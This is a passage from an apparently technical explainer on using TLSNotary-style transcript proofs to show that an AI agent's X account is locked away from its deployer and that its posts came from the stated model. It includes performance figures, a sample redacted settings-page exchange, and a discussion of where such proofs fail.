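| Time | 3.6 seconds on fibre, 10.4 on 5G, 14.5 on cable | 1.0 to 1.6 seconds | Up to 18 per cent more than a direct request |
| Extra data | About 30 MB uploaded before the session starts | The forwarded traffic and a proof | Very little |

The 30 MB upload accounts for most of the delay on slow connections. It takes about 52 seconds at 5 megabits per second and about one second at a gigabit per second. Distance also adds delay, because joint computation needs around 40 message exchanges during the handshake. With a round trip of 200 milliseconds, joint computation took 13.3 seconds and the proxy took 6.2.

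TLSNotary's developers projected an upload of 25 MB per session, plus 10 MB for each kilobyte sent and 40 KB for each kilobyte received. If Magpie sent a 2 KB request and received a 50 KB settings page, it would upload 25 + 20 + 2 = 47 MB. An agent in a data centre can easily upload that much once a day. It would be less practical for 1,000 followers to act as verifiers themselves, since Magpie would have to upload 47 GB and make 1,000 requests to X for the page. Most followers would therefore have to rely on a notary.

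TLSNotary's lack of support for TLS 1.3 could become a more serious problem. Celi, in *Commitments and zero-knowledge attestations over TLS 1.3*, cites Cloudflare figures that put version 1.3 at 63 per cent of secure traffic and version 1.2 at 8.7 per cent. *TrustedARI* (2026) gives over 96 per cent for the design of version 1.3, which the newer QUIC protocol also uses. TLSNotary still works with many websites because they still accept version 1.2. If X stopped accepting it, Magpie could no longer produce these proofs. *TLSNotary*, the roadmap from PSE, the lab behind the project, listed work on version 1.3 as paused in May 2026 and a production-ready release as planned for the second half of the year.

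DECO outlines a way to support TLS 1.3, and Celi and colleagues have built a prototype, DiStefano, that supports it. DiStefano lets a client commit to the encrypted data but doesn't yet include the zero-knowledge proofs about its contents. Celi also writes that researchers have shown some of DECO's cryptographic components to be insecure, so the 2019 design isn't safe to implement as written.

### A settings page with two gaps

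Suppose Magpie has just changed its X password and removed the deployer's connected apps, but hasn't yet authorised its own. Ada wants to check that the account has no phone number, no connected apps and only one open session. Magpie requests the account's settings with a notary's help and shows her the following. The page format is invented, "social.example" stands for X, and a real platform might spread the information over several pages.

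```
GET /settings/access?check=<Ada's challenge> HTTP/1.1
Host: social.example
Cookie: session=[32 bytes hidden]
Accept-Encoding: identity
Connection: close

HTTP/1.1 200 OK
Date: Mon, 05 Oct 2026 13:22:07 GMT
Content-Type: application/json

{"account_id": "1840000000000000001",
 "email": "[19 bytes hidden]",
 "phone": null,
 "connected_apps": [],
 "sessions": [{"current": true}]}
```

The notary has signed commitments that cover every byte of this exchange, including the hidden ones. Magpie reveals everything except the value of the session cookie, which would let Ada into the account, and the email address, which strangers could use to send Magpie fraudulent messages. Ada can see how long the two values are. Magpie uses the line "Accept-Encoding: identity" to ask the server not to compress its reply, because compression would prevent Magpie from revealing individual fields in readable form.

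The certificate that Magpie provides identifies the website. In the text that Magpie reveals, the account number shows whose settings these are, and Ada's challenge shows that the session took place after she sent it. Ada can also compare the date in the reply with the separate time in the notary's record.

The proof could still mislead Ada if Magpie revealed only the three lines she asked about. Zhang and colleagues give the example of Bob, who wants to exaggerate his bank balance. He sends customer service a message containing a false balance, opens the message during the same session and reveals only that text. The bank's server did send that text, but as part of Bob's own message. A deployer could similarly put "phone": null in the agent's profile description. To rule this out, Ada needs to know where the text appeared on the page.

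According to Celi, a proof about a single field would have to establish that the reply follows the rules of its format, that the field is at the top level, and that its value has the right type. Proving all this in zero knowledge takes a lot of computation. Magpie avoids most of it by revealing the rest of the page, so that Ada can work out the structure herself. She should compare the page with the settings of her own account, because a hidden gap could contain more than one field. She also needs to see both ends of each list, because a fragment that mentions one session doesn't show that there are no others.

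The hidden email address is the weakest part of this example, because the three facts Ada asked about could all be true while the deployer still owns the linked mailbox. Magpie could instead reveal the part after the @ sign, which would identify the provider. It could also publish a commitment to the full address:

C = SHA-256(address ‖ r)

Here *r* is a random number that stops Ada from hashing likely addresses until one matches. If Magpie puts *C* in its enclave quote as a commitment to the address of the mailbox it controls, it can prove in zero knowledge that the settings page contains the same address. TLSNotary can already prove that a commitment matches hidden text, and another proof system can use that commitment to prove further facts about the text. If Ada trusts the quote, she would learn that the enclave controls the linked mailbox.

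### The deployer can produce the same proof

TLSNotary's introduction lists "You have access to an account" among the things a user can prove. This causes trouble for a lockout, because the deployer may be that user:

1. The deployer logs in to the agent's account on a laptop.
2. They remove the phone number, the connected apps and all other sessions.
3. They request the settings page with an honest notary's help and hide the cookie and email address.
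4. They give the proof to Ada and say that Magpie made it.

The notary and X have both behaved correctly, and the proof is genuine. The one open session belongs to the deployer. If the page also showed a password change at 13:20, Ada would still not know who had chosen the new password.

Magpie can connect the proof to its enclave by putting a commitment to its session cookie in a quote and proving that the same cookie appears in the request. This would show that the enclave had the listed session, but Ada would again be relying on the quote. A deployer who knows the password also doesn't need to keep a session open and could log in after the check.

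The proof also covers only what the page lists at that moment. If X shows passkeys and delegated users elsewhere, Magpie needs to prove those pages too. Some ways into an account, such as a copied backup code, may not appear on any page. And the deployer can choose when to request a proof, so Ada can learn little from a clean page on Monday about the account's state on Sunday or Tuesday.

A TLS transcript proof can therefore show the account state that X reported, but not who caused it. To learn who chose the password, Ada needs evidence about the program that submitted it, which must come from an enclave quote and the published code.

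### When is it worth adding to a quote?

If Magpie's hardware and code both work, a notary's proof adds very little to Magpie's own takeover record, so the proof's value depends on what Ada doubts.

| Ada's doubt | What a notary's proof adds |
|---|---|
| The program misreads X's pages or prints fixed results | She can read X's reply herself |
| The program connected to a copy of X's website | She can check the real site's certificate |
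| The deployer forged the quote | She knows that the reply is real, but the deployer may have requested it |
| The program leaks its password | Nothing |
| The settings page leaves out a way into the account | Nothing |

The proof is most useful in the first case. If an outdated program mistakes a missing list for an empty one, Ada can see the mistake in X's reply and doesn't have to find it in the code. She still has to read the code that generates and stores the password.

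If her doubts are about the hardware, the notary must not depend on the same hardware. Suppose there is a 1 in 20 chance that the deployer can forge a quote, and a 1 in 20 chance that they can get a false signature from the notary. If these risks are independent, the chance that the deployer can fake the settings page in both pieces of evidence is

1/20 × 1/20 = 1/400

If the notary's only safeguard is an Intel TDX enclave on the deployer's own server, the interposer that defeats Magpie's enclave may defeat the notary's too. The chance is then close to 1 in 20. Moving the notary to AMD hardware would not help much, because TEE.fail also works on AMD. It is better to have an unrelated organisation run the notary on its own servers, even without enclaves. Neither calculation applies to the claim that the deployer doesn't know the password, since the notary provides no evidence about that.

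Running an independent notary inside an enclave can still make it harder for a dishonest employee to misuse the signing key. Grigor and colleagues ran the same notary with and without Intel TDX. TDX raised the average total time for a 32-message session from 136 to 152 seconds, or by about 12 per cent.

### Proving which model wrote a post

In *VET Your Agent*, Grigor and colleagues instead use transcript proofs to let readers check that an agent's output came from the stated model and tools, even if the host operator is dishonest. With an attested account, a deployer who controls the address of the language model can still write the agent's posts, and their framework, VET, would address this weakness.

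Each agent has an Agent Identity Document, which lists its language model, its tools and how to verify each. For a model the agent reaches over the internet, the document gives the provider's address, the notary's public key and hashes of the code that builds requests and interprets replies. The agent's identifier is a hash of the whole document, so the deployer can't change the model's address without changing the identifier.

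To check a post, a reader verifies the notary's signature and the provider's domain, confirms that the request and reply fit the code listed in the document, and compares the post with the text in the model's reply. If the agent used other tools, their results need proofs too. The reader has to trust every proof method the agent relies on, because an attacker who can defeat one of them can falsify part of the record. The framework also assumes that the model's provider is honest and doesn't collude with the host.

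The team tested this with five models. A direct request provided the baseline, and an enclave that forwarded requests provided a second comparison. Each entry is the average time in seconds for one message:

| Model | Direct | Through an enclave | With a notary, 1st message | With a notary, 32nd message |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 2.18 | 2.29 | 3.30 | 7.30 |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 1.80 | 1.97 | 2.46 | 6.61 |
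| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 4.59 | 4.68 | 5.34 | 8.86 |
| Mistral 3B | 0.75 | 0.76 | 1.33 | 5.94 |
| Mistral 8B | 0.90 | 1.06 | 1.59 | 6.03 |

The paper describes the overhead as typically less than three times the direct call. That holds for the first message, but by the 32nd message four of the five models took more than three times as long. The delay grows because each request contains the whole conversation so far. It depends mainly on the amount of text, so newer models shouldn't change the pattern much. The agent was also only about 5 milliseconds from the team's own notaries on a very fast network, so an agent on a home connection would wait longer.

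A simpler version kept one connection open for the whole conversation. It needed almost 10 seconds to set up a session of six messages and couldn't handle longer ones. The faster version opens a new connection for each message and prepares it while the model is answering the previous one. The public notary in the tests accepted at most 4 KB from the agent and 16 KB from the server per session, so a 50 KB settings page wouldn't have fitted. TLSNotary (2026) has since reported that a later release of its software runs 8 to 16 per cent faster.

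The team also built a trading agent, VeriTrade, which gets public market data through an enclave and uses a notary for its requests to Claude Haiku 4.5. A trading decision took 5.8 seconds with the notary and 4.2 seconds when an enclave handled these requests instead. They chose the notary because the requests contain an API key and possibly private instructions. The extra 1.6 seconds hardly matters for an agent that trades or posts every half hour.

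VET doesn't lock anyone out of an account. A deployer who still has the X password can publish a post without a proof, and only readers who look for the proof will notice it is missing. The deployer can also present an old proof as new, because the design doesn't guarantee freshness. Anyone who steals the notary's signing key can forge proofs for any agent that relies on that notary.

A dishonest host can also choose which genuine outputs to publish. Suppose Magpie's deployer asks the model for 50 posts and publishes the only one that praises a cryptocurrency they own. The proof for that post is valid, and readers never see the other 49. Combining VET with an enclave would make this harder. The measured program could ask the model once, record the request in a public log before it sees the reply, and publish whatever comes back. The deployer could still stop the program before it publishes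 an unwelcome reply, but the log would then contain a request with no matching post.
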